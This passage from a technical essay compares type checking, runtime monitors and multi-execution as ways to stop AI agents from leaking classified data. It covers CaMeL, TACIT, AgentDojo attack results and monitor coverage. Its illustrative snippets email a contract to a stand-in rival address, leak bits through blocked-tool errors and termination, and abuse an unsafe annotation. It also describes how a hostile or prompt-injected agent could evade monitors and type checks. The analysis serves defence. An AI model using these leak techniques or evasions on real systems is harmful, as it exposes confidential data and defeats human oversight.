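The rule rejects some programs that leak nothing, such as one that emails "received" in both branches of `if penalty`. The theorem also requires a deterministic language, because a program that assigns a random number to a public variable can end differently on two runs with the same inputs. A language model's output is usually partly random, so a guarantee for an agent's tools has to allow for this, for example by comparing runs in which the random choices are the same.

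### Stopping inside a secret branch

Monitors can also prevent the leak by restricting when labels may change. *Efficient purely-dynamic information flow analysis* (Austin and Flanagan, 2009) proposed a check, later known as no-sensitive-upgrade, that stops a program when it tries to assign to a public variable inside a secret branch. If the contract has a penalty clause, the program above stops at `temp = 1`, before it sends anything. If there is no clause, the program skips that assignment, runs to the end and emails "no".

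A competitor who expects an email can still tell the two cases apart, because no email arrives if there is a clause. The monitor still counts as sound because it guarantees only termination-insensitive noninterference, a weaker policy that lets the public outputs of two runs differ if one run produces the beginning of the other's output and then nothing more. The theorem of Volpano and colleagues has a similar gap because it covers only runs that finish. But their checker rejects this program before the program can read the contract, so the competitor learns nothing here.

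No-sensitive-upgrade also stops harmless programs:

```
note = ""
if penalty:
    note = "Check the penalty clause."
save_classified("contracts/notes.txt", note)
```

The monitor stops the program when it assigns to `note`, even though the note goes only into a classified file. In a second paper, *Permissive Dynamic Information Flow Analysis* (2009), Austin and Flanagan describe a monitor that allows such an assignment but marks the variable, here `note`, as partially leaked, meaning that its label could be public in another run. This monitor stops the program only if a later condition depends on a marked variable. The program could therefore finish, while the leaking one would stop at `if temp != 1`, though again only if the contract has a penalty clause.

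### Fixed and changing labels

*From dynamic to static and back* (Sabelfeld and Russo, 2009) showed that a monitor can control implicit flows in a simple language without static analysis. Researchers had long doubted this because a monitor follows only one path through the program. Sabelfeld and Russo's monitor guarantees termination-insensitive noninterference, as a type system in Denning's style does. It gives each variable a fixed label and blocks every assignment to a public variable inside a secret branch. If two runs take different branches because of a secret, each either leaves the public variables unchanged in its branch or stops, so their public outputs can differ only in where they end.

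With fixed labels, the monitor also accepts more than the type system. Suppose that `urgent` is public:

```
if urgent:
    send_email("sales@rival.example", contract_text)
else:
    send_email("sales@rival.example", "We will reply on Monday.")
```

The type checker rejects this program because one branch mails the contract. The monitor allows every run in which `urgent` is false.

Fixed labels are impractical for much ordinary code, where a variable may hold part of a contract at one point and a greeting later. Agents that write Python don't normally declare a secrecy level for each variable either. An analysis that lets labels change during the program is called flow-sensitive. Static analyses of this kind exist, and they accept more programs than those with fixed labels. One might expect monitors to benefit at least as much, but Russo and Sabelfeld prove that they don't. No monitor with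 changing labels can meet all four of these conditions:

- It judges each command without looking at the commands that come after it.
- It ignores the contents of branches that the run does not take.
- It guarantees termination-insensitive noninterference.
- It leaves unchanged every program that a standard flow-sensitive type system accepts.

The proof changes the leaking program above by replacing `answer = "no"` with `pass`, which does nothing. The changed program always emails "yes", and the type system accepts it, so the monitor must let it run. If the contract has a penalty clause, the two programs differ only in a branch that the run skips. The monitor ignores that branch, so it must let the leaking program email "yes" too.

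Now suppose we restore that line and replace `temp = 1` with `pass`. The program always emails "no", and the type system accepts this version too. If the contract has no penalty clause, this program again differs from the leaking one only in a skipped branch, so the monitor must let the leaking program email "no". The leaking program can therefore send a different answer for each kind of contract, which violates the third condition.

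When labels can change, any sound monitor of this kind rejects some programs that the type system accepts, though it may accept others that the type system rejects. Russo and Sabelfeld do not say how many useful programs fall into each group, which is what a developer would most want to know.

### Looking at the other branch

The way out is to drop the second condition. In the hybrid monitors that Russo and Sabelfeld describe, the monitor scans the branch that the program skips at each secret condition, and labels every variable that the branch could change as secret. For the leaking program this works as follows:

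- With a penalty clause, `temp` becomes secret through its assignment. The program then skips `answer = "no"`, but the monitor finds the line in the skipped branch and labels `answer` secret.
- Without a clause, the monitor finds `temp = 1` in the skipped branch and labels `temp` secret. The assignment to `answer` then happens inside a secret branch, so `answer` becomes secret too.

The monitor blocks the email in both cases, so the competitor receives nothing. Russo and Sabelfeld prove that such monitors are sound and accept every program the flow-sensitive type system accepts. The monitors also accept some programs that the type system rejects, such as a loop that prints a counter on each pass and overwrites the counter with a secret at the end of the last pass.

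The monitor's response to a forbidden output can also leak the secret. If the program sends an email only when `penalty` is true, and the monitor replaces that email with a standard notice, the notice's arrival reveals the clause. Russo and Sabelfeld therefore allow default values, such as this notice, only outside secret branches. Inside them, the monitor has to suppress the output or stop the program.

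A hybrid monitor needs the program's text as well as its actions. A harness that interprets agent code has this text, but a guard on a single tool does not.

### Running the program once per secrecy level

Devriese and Piessens (2010), in *Noninterference Through Secure Multi-Execution*, avoid labels on variables altogether. With two secrecy levels, their system runs the program twice:

- The public run receives a default value in place of each secret input, and only this run can send public outputs.
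- The secret run receives the real inputs, but the system discards its public outputs and keeps only the secret ones.

If the default for `penalty` is false, the public run of the leaking program always emails "no". The secret run computes the real answer, but its email never leaves the machine. Public outputs can't depend on the contract because the run that produces them never receives it.

The method also preserves the inputs and outputs of any run that would normally finish, provided the program satisfies noninterference, including in whether it terminates. This is consistent with the limits on exact detection because the method never detects a violation. It changes what the program receives, just as the filtered directory listing did for the secret file. *Transparent IFC Enforcement* (2020) reports that all known methods that guarantee noninterference without false alarms run the program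 several times.

Silently changing how insecure programs behave can cause problems for agents. Suppose the assistant emails a supplier to say whether their contract allows late delivery. The public run works from a default contract, so the supplier may get a false answer that looks genuine. Devriese and Piessens suggest warning the user when the secret run would have sent something different.

Tool calls also need special treatment, since a payment must not happen twice. If a call both acts on the world and returns a result, the system makes it once, in the run at the call's own level, and passes the result to any run at a higher level. If a secret run reaches a public call that the public run never makes, it will wait forever for the result. The proofs cover a simple deterministic language. Devriese and Piessens see no fundamental obstacle to randomness, but say a formal proof for it would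 be considerably harder.

### CaMeL and TACIT

The agent systems CaMeL and TACIT illustrate the difference between tracking data and tracking code. CaMeL, which Edoardo Debenedetti and others published in 2025, attaches taint to data as the program runs. Before any code runs, TACIT checks which capabilities that code can use. This description of CaMeL follows the comparison in Odersky and colleagues' paper on TACIT.

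Both systems keep sensitive or untrusted data away from the model that plans the work. CaMeL uses one model to plan and another to read data, and its own interpreter runs the plan and coordinates the two. The plans use a subset of Python without function definitions or recursion. TACIT has a single agent that works in an ordinary loop of tool calls and can use nearly all of Scala. A separate, trusted model processes classified text.

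Odersky and colleagues argue that CaMeL could lift its restrictions only with a great deal of computation. Precisely analyzing how data flows through functions that take other functions as arguments is EXPTIME-complete, so in the worst case the time required grows exponentially with program size. TACIT avoids this analysis because type annotations specify what each function may hold, and the compiler checks each function separately. However, the argument applies to guarantees made before the program runs. An interpreter can label values as they pass through any function, and it needs such an analysis mainly to work out what a skipped branch might have changed.

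A second argument is that a value loses its taint once it enters a model's context as ordinary text, whereas TACIT never puts classified text there. Labels on individual values do have this weakness, but a monitor can also label the whole context, as Tether does.

Odersky and colleagues also ran TACIT on AgentDojo with the two models from CaMeL's evaluation. Each cell below gives the share of user tasks completed, followed by the number of successful attacks. The difference is TACIT's task score minus CaMeL's, in percentage points.

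| Model | System | Banking | Office work | Slack | Travel |
|---|---|---|---|---|---|
| Gemini 2.5 Pro | CaMeL | 52.8%; 0 of 144 | 53.8%; 0 of 574 | 48.6%; 0 of 105 | 1.4%; 0 of 140 |
| | TACIT | 56.9%; 0 of 144 | 50.5%; 0 of 574 | 40.0%; 0 of 105 | 64.3%; 0 of 140 |
| | Difference | +4.1 | −3.3 | −8.6 | +62.9 |
| o4-mini-high | CaMeL | 62.5%; 1 of 144 | 81.4%; 0 of 574 | 68.6%; 0 of 105 | 74.3%; 0 of 140 |
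| | TACIT | 59.0%; 0 of 144 | 52.9%; 0 of 574 | 47.6%; 0 of 105 | 68.6%; 1 of 140 |
| | Difference | −3.5 | −28.5 | −21.0 | −5.7 |

The paper describes the task scores as "comparable", but several of these numbers don't seem to support that. With o4-mini-high, CaMeL did better in all four areas, by 28.5 points in office work and 21 in Slack. With Gemini, TACIT scored far higher in travel, but only because CaMeL completed almost no tasks there. CaMeL scored 74.3 percent in travel with o4-mini-high, which suggests that something specific to Gemini went wrong. The CaMeL scores come from its own paper rather than from new runs, so differences in prompts and setup may explain part of the gaps.

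TACIT's interface may explain some of its low scores. In the version for AgentDojo, the functions that read emails, files and Slack messages return wrapped values, but those that send messages or money accept only ordinary ones. For example, an agent can show the user a bill but has no direct way to pay the amount on it. TACIT scored highest with both models in travel, where most functions return ordinary values such as hotel names and prices.

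Each system let through one attack in 1,926 trials, so the attack results don't show which is more secure. In the attack that TACIT let through, the attacker had planted a recommendation for another hotel in the reviews of the one the user wanted. The agent booked the right hotel but quoted the reviews, and AgentDojo counted the mention of the other hotel as a successful attack. The comparison includes no runs without a defence, so it doesn't show how many attacks would have failed anyway. AgentDojo also doesn't test noninterference, because it checks only whether the attacker's goal was met.

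### Can a monitor enforce local purity?

TACIT's protection of contracts depends on local purity: the function that agent code passes to `map` must have no side effects. Odersky and colleagues write that such properties are "beyond the reach of purely runtime enforcement". Yet a monitor could simply block all tools while the function handles the secret:

```
def sealed_map(secret, f):
    tools.block_all()
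    try:
        result = f(secret.value)
    finally:
        tools.unblock_all()
    return Classified(result)
```

If `f` tries to send the contract, the email tool raises an error and nothing leaves. But the error itself can leak information:

```
def probe(text):
    if "penalty" in text:
        send_email("sales@rival.example", "x")   # blocked
    return ""

sealed_map(contract, probe)
send_email("sales@rival.example", "done")
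```

If the contract mentions a penalty, the error ends the program before the last line. Otherwise, the competitor receives "done". Each such program reveals one bit, so a hostile agent could work out a price below a million euros by using about 20 programs to halve the range repeatedly. TACIT's compiler would reject `probe` whatever the contract contains, so the rejection reveals nothing about the contract.

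The monitor can close this gap by catching the error inside `sealed_map` and returning an empty wrapped result. The rest of the program then runs the same way whether or not `f` broke the rule. TACIT already handles ordinary exceptions this way, because its types don't rule them out.

Blocking the tools is not enough, because `f` could still copy the contract into a variable outside the function for the program to send later. To prevent this, the harness could run `f` in a separate process that has no tools, receives a copy of the text and can only return a result. Odersky and colleagues note in an appendix that a language whose functions could never hold capabilities would have local purity without tracking capabilities in types. They consider this very restrictive, but a harness would need to impose this restriction only on functions that handle secrets.

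The claim therefore holds only in a narrower sense. A monitor can keep a function from having effects in every run, but it can't establish in advance that the function will never attempt one. The compiler can report exactly what is wrong with a function, because its error message doesn't depend on any contract, and the agent can then correct the code. The monitor has to hide the reason for a failure from the agent. If a function works on 99 contracts and tries to write to a log on the hundredth, the agent gets another wrapped result and never learns that this one is empty. However, the monitor accepts functions that hold a capability but never use it, and the compiler rejects them.

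### Timing and termination

Termination-insensitive noninterference can permit more than a one-bit leak. Suppose that `price` is a secret whole number below a million, and that `publish` sends a number to a public website:

```
for guess in range(1_000_000):
    publish(guess)
    while guess == price:
        pass
```

The program posts numbers on the website, counting up to the secret price, and then hangs, so the last number posted is the price. The type system of Volpano and colleagues accepts this program because the loop that hangs doesn't assign to any public variable. The hybrid monitors accept it for the same reason. The policy allows this leak because, for any two prices, the output of one run is the beginning of the other's.

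Russo and Sabelfeld defend the weaker policy partly by arguing that such attacks are slow. An attacker can't learn a secret this way in time polynomial in its length, so a random 128-bit key is safe in practice. But an attacker needs at most a million messages to learn a price below a million, and only one to learn whether there is a penalty clause. Russo and Sabelfeld add that termination is hard to control, because even a program without endless loops can crash, for instance by running out of memory.

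Programs can also leak secrets through their running time. Devriese and Piessens give a JavaScript example that runs a loop of 10,000 steps only if a secret is set, measures the time and stores the result in a public variable. Odersky and colleagues exclude timing and termination from TACIT's guarantee. A function inside `map` could spend several seconds on contracts with a penalty clause and finish at once on others. The compiler would accept it because it is pure, and the agent would only have to time the reply. `sealed_map` has the same weakness. A harness could return every result after the same fixed time, but quick programs would then take as long as slow ones.

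Secure multi-execution closes both channels, provided that the public run never has to wait for the secret one. In an agent system, the harness would have to return the public output to the agent while the secret run was still in progress, without revealing when that run finished. A simple schedule completes the public run first, but then the secret run never starts if the public run never ends.

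### Releasing a secret on purpose

Noninterference is often too strict. The employer may want to tell a supplier the total due under a classified contract, and this message has to depend on the contract. Both methods then need an exception, which researchers call declassification.

In a type system, the exception could be an operation that turns a secret value into a public one. Volpano and colleagues discuss a similar operator that declares untrusted data trustworthy. They conclude that their theorem no longer holds for a language that includes it, and they find it difficult to say what the analysis would then guarantee. Monitors and multi-execution face the same problem, because a program that releases a secret no longer satisfies noninterference. Rafnsson and Sabelfeld, in *Secure Multi-Execution: Fine-grained, Declassification-aware, and Transparent*, extend Devriese and Piessens's technique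 to programs that deliberately release some secrets.

TACIT's design limits who may release a secret. Its description includes a `reveal` method, which unwraps a classified value but requires a capability that the agent doesn't have. A user with the right clearance could have it. The design doesn't determine whether a particular value is safe to release.

That depends on who computed the value. A hostile agent that wrote the function for calculating the total could encode part of the contract in the total's digits, and the result would still look like an ordinary amount. The employer could instead supply a trusted function that reads the total from the contract and releases only that. A run-time check could add a second safeguard, such as a daily limit on how many values the agent may release. Odersky and colleagues consider TACIT's library the natural place for checks on declassification,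 but leave them to future work.

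## What does a guarantee for all inputs leave out?

A type checker's guarantee for all inputs depends on type soundness, a theorem about the programming language, and holds only where the theorem's assumptions hold.

### What a soundness theorem promises

Xu, Bračevac and colleagues (2026), in *System Capybara*, prove such a theorem for a small language that models Scala's capture checking. In simplified form:

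```
if    C; Γ ⊢ t : E                          (the checker accepts t)
and   H | t runs to a result a with trace τ
then  τ uses only what C permits, and a behaves as E requires
```

Γ lists the variables and capabilities that the surrounding program provides, and H is a starting memory that contains them. C is the set of capabilities that the program t may use, according to the checker. A companion theorem covers runs that haven't finished and shows that an accepted program never gets stuck, for example by trying to read memory it has already freed.

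Both theorems hold regardless of who wrote the program or what the memory contains, so they cover an attacker's code and contracts full of injected instructions. For a function that agent code passes to `map`, C is empty, and the function can touch only memory cells it creates itself.

The theorems don't cover rejected programs, many of which may be harmless, or running time, so timing leaks remain possible. They also apply only to a formal language whose programs can read, write, create and free memory cells, but can't use a network or send email. Applying the theorems to `httpPost` requires treating the network as another cell that code can reach only through a capability, which is reasonable but isn't part of the proof.

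### How far the proofs for Scala reach

When Odersky and colleagues presented TACIT, the machine-checked proofs covered the basic rules of capture checking but not safe mode. Two July 2026 papers from the same group narrowed this gap, but as of December 2026 nobody appears to have published the semantic proof that safe mode needs.

Xu and colleagues give a semantic proof. An older kind, the syntactic proof, shows that each step of a run turns one well-typed program into another. It covers only code that follows the typing rules throughout, and a harness's library may have to break them in places. A semantic proof defines what it means for code to behave as its type requires, then shows that code following the rules behaves this way. The guarantee can still cover code that breaks the rules if a separate proof shows that the code behaves as its type requires. Xu and colleagues give the example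 of a function that tests whether two memory cells are different and, if so, writes to both in parallel. The typing rules reject it because they don't take the test into account, but it can be proved safe.

The other paper, *Classifying Capabilities (Extended Version)* (Pham, Bračevac and colleagues, 2026), has a machine-checked proof that a program's result can reach only those control capabilities that its type lists. Control capabilities are those that control the flow of a program, such as permission to throw an exception.

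Much of Scala is still outside these proofs. Xu and colleagues leave out classes, exceptions and threads that outlive the call that started them. They verified the core language by machine, but they verified the translation into it from a more Scala-like language only on paper. They also don't prove that the Scala compiler follows their rules.

A full proof for safe mode could resemble the one in *Griotte* (2026), which concerns a machine with capabilities built into its hardware. Its main theorem gives a specification that any unknown code on the machine satisfies. Combining this theorem with proofs about known code gives a result for the whole system. In TACIT, the agent's program would be the unknown code and the library would be the known code.

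### The trusted base

TACIT's trusted base consists of the Scala compiler, the runtime that executes the compiled code, the capability library and, if the employer uses one, the local model that reads classified text. A bug in the compiler could make it accept a program that the rules forbid. A bug in the runtime could let a correctly checked program escape, which is one reason Odersky and colleagues recommend also running TACIT inside a sandbox.

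The reusable part of the library is about 1,000 lines of Scala. Its developers assert what its types are, and they can be wrong. In Scala's standard library, `Try` runs a piece of code and stores either its result or the exception it raised. In the version for capture checking, the signature declared that a `Try` holds no capabilities. Pham and colleagues point out that this was a mistake, because reading the result can throw the stored exception again, which requires permission to throw. The compiler hadn't checked this part of the library because the language had no way to express the right type. With their extension, the compiler checks 81.7 percent of the standard library's lines for captures, up from 66.7 percent.

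TACIT relies on `Try` to contain exceptions. The mistake did not in itself expose contracts, but a similar one elsewhere could. The riskiest place is code marked `@assumeSafe`, which the compiler exempts from the rules of safe mode. Scala's documentation gives the example of a cache that stores a function's earlier results in a hidden variable. This is safe if the cache holds nothing else and the function always gives the same result for the same argument. The programmer has to verify both conditions. Here is a similar module that isn't safe:

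```
@assumeSafe
object Recent:
  @untrackedCaptures private var last = ""
  def swap(text: String): String =
    val previous = last
    last = text
    previous
```

`swap` stores a text and returns the one stored before it. The annotation hides the variable from the checker, so the checker treats `swap` as pure, and an agent can call `contract.map(text => Recent.swap(text))`. The agent can then call `Recent.swap("")` outside `map` and get the contract as ordinary text. Both calls compile, so one wrong annotation removes the protection from every contract.

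Monitors have a trusted base too, and a machine-checked proof doesn't remove it. *PerMIT* (2026) describes a system that protects an agent's stored memory, with proofs in Lean, a program that verifies mathematical proofs. The paper notes that Lean certifies the formal statements but not that they match a deployed harness. *Alignment Contracts for Agentic Security Systems* (2026) makes the same distinction. Its Lean proofs don't establish, for instance, that the hooks in an operating system's kernel catch every action. However, a monitor doesn't depend on the agent's language having a sound type system, and some type systems have turned out to be unsound.

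### A hole in Java and Scala

*Java and Scala's Type Systems are Unsound* (Amin and Tate, 2016) presents short programs that turn a value of any type into a value of any other type without a cast. The programs use `null`, which both languages accepted as a value of almost every type. A programmer can write a type whose values serve as evidence that, for example, every number is a string. Only `null` can have this type, but the compiler accepts it as evidence and lets the program use numbers as strings.

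A hole like this would let an agent give a function that posts a contract the type of a pure function, without the unchecked cast that safe mode forbids. The Java virtual machine, which runs the compiled programs of both languages, was not affected. It makes its own checks while a program runs, so using a number as text causes an error. It couldn't detect a false capture set this way, because the compiler removes capture sets before the program runs.

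Java compilers from version 9 on reject some of the original Java examples, and a later checker for null errors catches the rest, although variants with extra annotations still pass that checker and crash. Scala's safe mode compiles agent code with "explicit nulls", a setting under which `null` is no longer a value of ordinary types. Amin and Tate's programs need `null` to be such a value, so the setting blocks them, but it doesn't prove that no other trick exists. Biały and Warchoł (2026) mention in *Making the AI agents safe with Scala* that developers have also used frontier models to look for exploits in TACIT.

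### Amounts and history

Even a perfect compiler can enforce only what types can express. Suppose that the payment tool has this signature:

```
def pay(to: Account, euros: Int): Unit
```

Policy B limits payments to 1,000 euros a day per recipient. Ordinary types can't express this limit because they describe what kind of value something is, but not which value it is or what has happened so far. `Int` covers both 350 and 90,000, and `pay` has the same type before and after the first payment.

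Types can now also exclude a whole category of capabilities. Capture sets used to list permitted capabilities one by one, but Pham and colleagues add tags, arranged in a tree. If the employer tags everything that moves money as `Payment`, the type `Invoice ->{any.except[Payment]} Boolean` describes a function that may use any capabilities except the ones with that tag. They reproduced all 59 examples of such exclusions that earlier researchers had collected from real software. The tags don't help with amounts, but there are three main remedies for that.

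**A budget capability.** The library can require a capability for each payment and compare the amount with the day's total when the program runs:

```
def pay(to: Account, euros: Int)(using Budget^): Unit
```

This is the same monitor as `guarded_pay`, but the compiler now ensures that agent code can't pay without a `Budget`, make its own or keep one after its block ends. Agent code needs almost no extra annotations because Scala passes the capability implicitly. The compiler needs no new kind of check, and the library makes one comparison per payment. A program can still fail after some of its payments have gone through. TACIT leaves spending limits like this one, along with checks on declassification, to future work.

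**Single-use tokens.** The harness could instead issue ten tokens a day for each recipient, each worth 100 euros. Scala's new separation checker, which Xu and colleagues built, lets a function use up its argument:

```
def pay100(consume token: AcmeToken^): Unit

pay100(t1)
pay100(t1)   // rejected: t1 is already used up
```

The compiler can now reject overspending before the first payment. But an invoice for 350 euros doesn't match the token denomination, and paying it with one-euro tokens would take 350 of them. A program that loops over invoices would probably keep its tokens in a list, and the checker doesn't let code directly use up part of a shared structure. The harness also has to record which tokens it has issued today, so it still needs a count at run time.

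Most of the annotations are in the library, and Xu and colleagues haven't measured how many annotations existing code would need. They also haven't proved that the rules are decidable. In practice, the compiler keeps a set of used-up capabilities and rejects any later use of them.

Strictly speaking, these tokens are affine, which means a program may use them at most once. Linear tokens, which a program must use exactly once, could help with policy C. If `pay` returned a linear "receipt due" value that only `file_receipt` accepts, the checker would reject a program that didn't call `file_receipt`. The checker could not prevent an accepted program from crashing before it filed the receipt.

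**Refinement types.** A refinement type adds a condition to an ordinary type. Bovel, Kunčak and Odersky (2026), in *First-Class Refinement Types for Scala*, built a prototype in which `Int with x % 2 == 0` is the type of even numbers. A payment function in their notation might look like this:

```
def pay(b: Budget)(euros: Int with euros <= b.left):
  {r: Budget with r.left == b.left - euros}
```

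It accepts only amounts that the budget `b` covers, and returns a new budget with the rest. The compiler doesn't know what earlier programs have spent, so it can't know `b.left`. It can require the agent's program to find out:

```
if invoice.amount <= b.left then pay(b)(invoice.amount)
```

Inside this branch the checker can assume the condition is true, so it can accept the payment. Without the test, it can't prove that the budget is large enough. The comparison still happens at run time, but the compiler guarantees that it happens. Where the compiler can't prove a condition, the programmer can also request an automatic run-time check, which raises an exception if the condition is false.

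This signature doesn't enforce policy B by itself, because the program can keep the old budget `b` and spend it again. Enforcing the policy would also require each budget to be single-use. Bovel and colleagues leave the connection with capture checking to future work.

A solver decides whether one condition implies another. No solver can do this in every case, because a condition may call functions that never return. This one therefore rejects any implication it can't prove. It also assumes, without checking, that every function in a condition is pure and will finish, so the compiler gives no warning if a programmer uses an impure one. Bovel and colleagues verified the soundness proof by machine, but the proof covers a core language and not the solver.

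| Remedy | Annotations | Decidability | Left for run time |
|---|---|---|---|
| Budget capability | one extra parameter on each paying function | no new question for the compiler | every amount and total |
| Single-use tokens | markers in the library; number not measured | not proved; the compiler tracks used-up tokens | how many tokens the harness has issued today |
| Refinement types | conditions in signatures; tests in agent code | undecidable in general; the solver rejects what it can't prove | the budget at the start, and anything the solver can't prove |

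For policy B, the budget capability looks like the best choice. The other two are more complicated and still need a run-time count. Their advantage is that they can reject some bad programs before any money moves.

### Verifying programs against a contract

Meijer's proposal, as Odersky and colleagues summarise it, goes further than types. The harness would verify an agent's workflow against preconditions and postconditions, in the style of the verification language Dafny. A precondition must hold before a call, and a postcondition holds after it. For payments they could be:

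```
pay(to, euros)
  requires  spent[to] + euros <= 1000
  ensures   spent[to] = old spent[to] + euros
```

Suppose a program pays Acme 400 euros three times, with `spent` starting at zero. The first call's postcondition sets `spent` to 400, and the second's sets it to 800. The third call would require 1,200 to be at most 1,000, so the verifier rejects the program. It does this with an SMT solver, the kind of tool Progent uses to compare policies. Because the conditions describe how the total changes, they don't need tokens or a new budget after each payment.

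Loops are harder to verify. For a program that pays a list of invoices of unknown length, the verifier needs a loop invariant, a statement that is true before every pass, such as "no recipient has received more than 1,000 euros". Someone, presumably the model, has to write the invariant. Verification is undecidable in general, so the solver sometimes fails to prove that a correct program is correct. The proof also assumes that `spent` starts at the real total for the day and that no other program pays the same recipient in the meantime.

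Odersky and colleagues prefer types because precise specifications are often unavailable or impractical. AI Engineer's *Make the Agent Produce a Program Before It Can Act* (2026), a write-up of a later talk by Meijer, combines types with proofs. The agent has to produce a program with proofs that others can check, and the type system separates proposed actions from real effects. The model has to find the proof, which is much harder than checking it, as in proof-carrying code.

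VeriGuard, a system published in 2025, applies verification to the monitor instead of the agent's program. A language model turns the user's safety requirements into a specification and writes a policy function. A verifier then proves that the function meets the specification. At runtime, the function checks each action the agent proposes. The harness needs to verify only this function, however many programs the agent writes and in whatever language. The proof covers every input to the function, but it doesn't show that the specification matches what the user wanted.

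Writing the specification may be the weakest step. Dantas and colleagues call it the field's bottleneck. On one benchmark, language models translated descriptions into PDDL, a formal language for planning problems, and only 24.8 to 34.2 percent of the translations had the right meaning. Many of the wrong translations were still valid PDDL, which is dangerous because a verifier accepts them. Translating a payment limit is probably easier than translating a planning problem, and newer models may do better. Dantas and colleagues also give most of their review's main findings the lowest certainty rating.

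People also write wrong specifications. The precondition above accepts a payment of −500 euros, which lowers `spent` to −500 and then allows a payment of 1,500. The refinement type has the same flaw, and so does `guarded_pay` if the bank's tool accepts negative amounts. All three must also require a positive amount. No proof would have revealed the mistake, because it is in the statement to be proved.

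### Permission and intent

A specification can be free of such slips and still grant more than the task needs. To test TACIT on an airline's customer service tasks, Odersky and colleagues gave the agent this function:

```
def cancelReservation(reservationId: String): Reservation
```

Any program that passes text to the cancellation function is well-typed, even if it cancels a ticket against the airline's rules. A monitor with access only to this call and its argument couldn't detect the violation either. The cancellation gate that Reddy and colleagues tested worked because it looked up the booking.

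In LACUNA, excess permission can be even harder to notice. Generated code may use whatever is available where the call is made. If a developer opened a network connection for another purpose and left it available there, the generated code may use it too. Zhao and colleagues therefore count the developer's own program as part of the trusted base.

Tight permissions don't ensure that the agent makes the right choices either. Odersky and colleagues exclude correctness from their goals, since a program can pass every type check and still produce a wrong result. But they argue that a prompt injection can do real harm only by sending private data somewhere unauthorised or by triggering something outside the agent's capabilities. This seems too optimistic, since an assistant that pays the forged invoice leaks nothing and uses only a capability it needs. If the amount is within the daily limit, a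 monitor for policy B would also allow the payment.

An agent can also cause this kind of harm by mistake, without an attacker. According to AI Engineer, Meijer lost a file to Claude Code while distracted by preparing his slides. An agent that tidies a folder needs permission to delete files, and neither a type nor a simple rule identifies the file the user wanted to keep. With either types or monitors, the harness can ask the user before each deletion, but Odersky and colleagues warn that people tire of such questions and stop reading them.

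Some policies can't be stated exactly at all. The employer might forbid emails that contain personal data. The phrase "the engineer who left in March" identifies someone to a colleague and nobody to a stranger, so whether it counts depends on who reads it. With refinement types, a developer could still write:

```
def send_email(to: Address, body: String with !hasPersonalData(body)): Unit
```

This compiles, but the type means only that `hasPersonalData` returned false. The function can be wrong, and a monitor that calls it makes the same mistakes. Refinement types also require a condition to always give the same result for the same value, which a language model may not do. If `hasPersonalData` calls a language model, the checker would treat the first result as permanently true of the text, while a monitor can call the function again before each email.

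## Which of an agent's actions does each method see?

A type checker's guarantee holds for every input to the programs it accepts, but it doesn't cover anything the agent does outside those programs. "Coverage" can therefore mean either the share of a program's possible runs for which a guarantee holds or the share of routes from the agent to the outside world that pass through a checkpoint.

Suppose one branch of the assistant's program emails a contract to a competitor, and about one run in a thousand reaches that branch. A type checker rejects the program before its first run. A monitor on the email tool lets the program run and blocks the email when the program tries to send it. Either can prevent the leak, but with the monitor, nobody learns about the bad branch until a run reaches it.

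Suppose a colleague gives the assistant a second email tool without connecting it to the type checker or the monitor. Both guarantees still hold for the first tool but don't cover the second.

### Complete mediation

Security engineers call the condition on routes complete mediation. Saltzer and Schroeder defined it in their 1975 tutorial, *The Protection of Information in Computer Systems*: "Every access to every object must be checked for authority." They included access during start-up, recovery, shutdown and maintenance. They were also wary of systems that save time by remembering the result of an earlier check, because permissions may have changed. *ZeroGate* (2026) applies the condition to agents and lists retries, subprocesses and background workers among the routes that a gate must cover. It also warns developers not to include uncovered routes in their claims of coverage.

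Proofs about monitors usually assume complete mediation. The soundness theorem in *Alignment Contracts for Agentic Security Systems* holds even for a hostile agent, but only if the monitor receives every relevant event before that event takes effect. *Stop Means Stop* (2026) proves properties of a gate's decisions and leaves it to the developer to send every action through the gate. It provides a tool that searches the code for direct calls that skip the gate, which mainly catches accidental bypasses. *Causality Laundering* (2026) assumes that its monitor is the only connection between the model and the tool server, which is true only if the company sets it up that way.

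*Kairos* (2026) instead puts the agent behind an isolation layer, so that its only channels to the outside pass through the monitor. The monitor's coverage then no longer depends on which interface the agent uses.

For a typed harness, the corresponding condition is capability completeness, which Odersky and colleagues require. An effect that needs no capability doesn't appear in any type, so a library function that can send email without a capability is like an unguarded tool.

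### Fifteen paths and eight placements

*guardscope* (Toyoda, Leung and U, 2026) presents a framework for measuring how many routes a monitor covers. The paper lists 15 routes by which a harness can turn a model's decision into an effect. For example, the harness can run a function in its own memory, write a file, start another program, open a network connection, call a tool server, or hand the task to another agent.

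The paper then considers eight options for where to put a control, including having none, and works out from the design which paths each one checks. Some of the answers depend on how a company connects its systems. A network filter can also block a path without making a policy decision, and the paper counts this separately as prevention.

| Placement | Paths checked | Paths prevented | Depends on the set-up |
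|---|---|---|---|
| No control | 0 | 0 | 0 |
| Gateway in front of web-based tool servers | 1 | 0 | 3 |
| The same, with a filter on other network traffic | 1 | 1 | 4 |
| The same, with local tool servers also behind the gateway | 3 | 1 | 4 |
| The harness's own permission system | 5 | 0 | 1 |
| The same, with a gateway in front of web-based tool servers | 5 | 0 | 1 |
| Policy engine inside the harness process | 5 | 0 | 1 |
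| Operating system kernel | 13 | 0 | 1 |

A gateway is a proxy between the harness and its tool servers, so it checks only the calls that go through it. Controls inside the harness check more because the harness dispatches both local and remote tool calls. The kernel is the core of the operating system, and programs need it to open files, use the network or start other programs. In principle, a control in the kernel misses only functions that work entirely in the harness's memory, though whether it sees work that a separate service carries out later depends on the set-up. Five of the 15 paths pass no checkpoint outside the kernel.

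*Agentao* (Jin, Jiao and Tong, 2026) describes a harness that is an example of the permission-system placement. The harness decides whether to allow each proposed tool call, refuse it or ask the user. It applies the same decision process to local tools, tools from MCP servers and the tool calls of sub-agents, whose coverage guardscope lists as depending on the set-up. Jin and colleagues assume that the operating system and the host application work correctly, and they offer no formal guarantee.

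The numbers are counts of the kinds of paths, not of how often agents use them. If an office assistant's tools are all on web-based servers, a gateway that checks only one kind of path may check nearly everything the assistant does. The list may also be incomplete, because Toyoda and colleagues compiled it by studying existing harnesses and discussing candidates with two AI models.

Most of the classified systems have narrow coverage. Gateways were the largest group, and the only kernel-level policy control found was ActPlane, a research system.

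### What the test runs confirmed

Toyoda and colleagues also ran all eight placements with a real harness called Pi. A replay program made Pi carry out the same 15 actions each time, without a language model. Each control first had to refuse a forbidden action to show that it was working. During the run, a separate sensor recorded events in the kernel, and the researchers compared these with the control's own log. They used Microsoft's Agent Governance Toolkit as the gateway and ActPlane as the kernel control.

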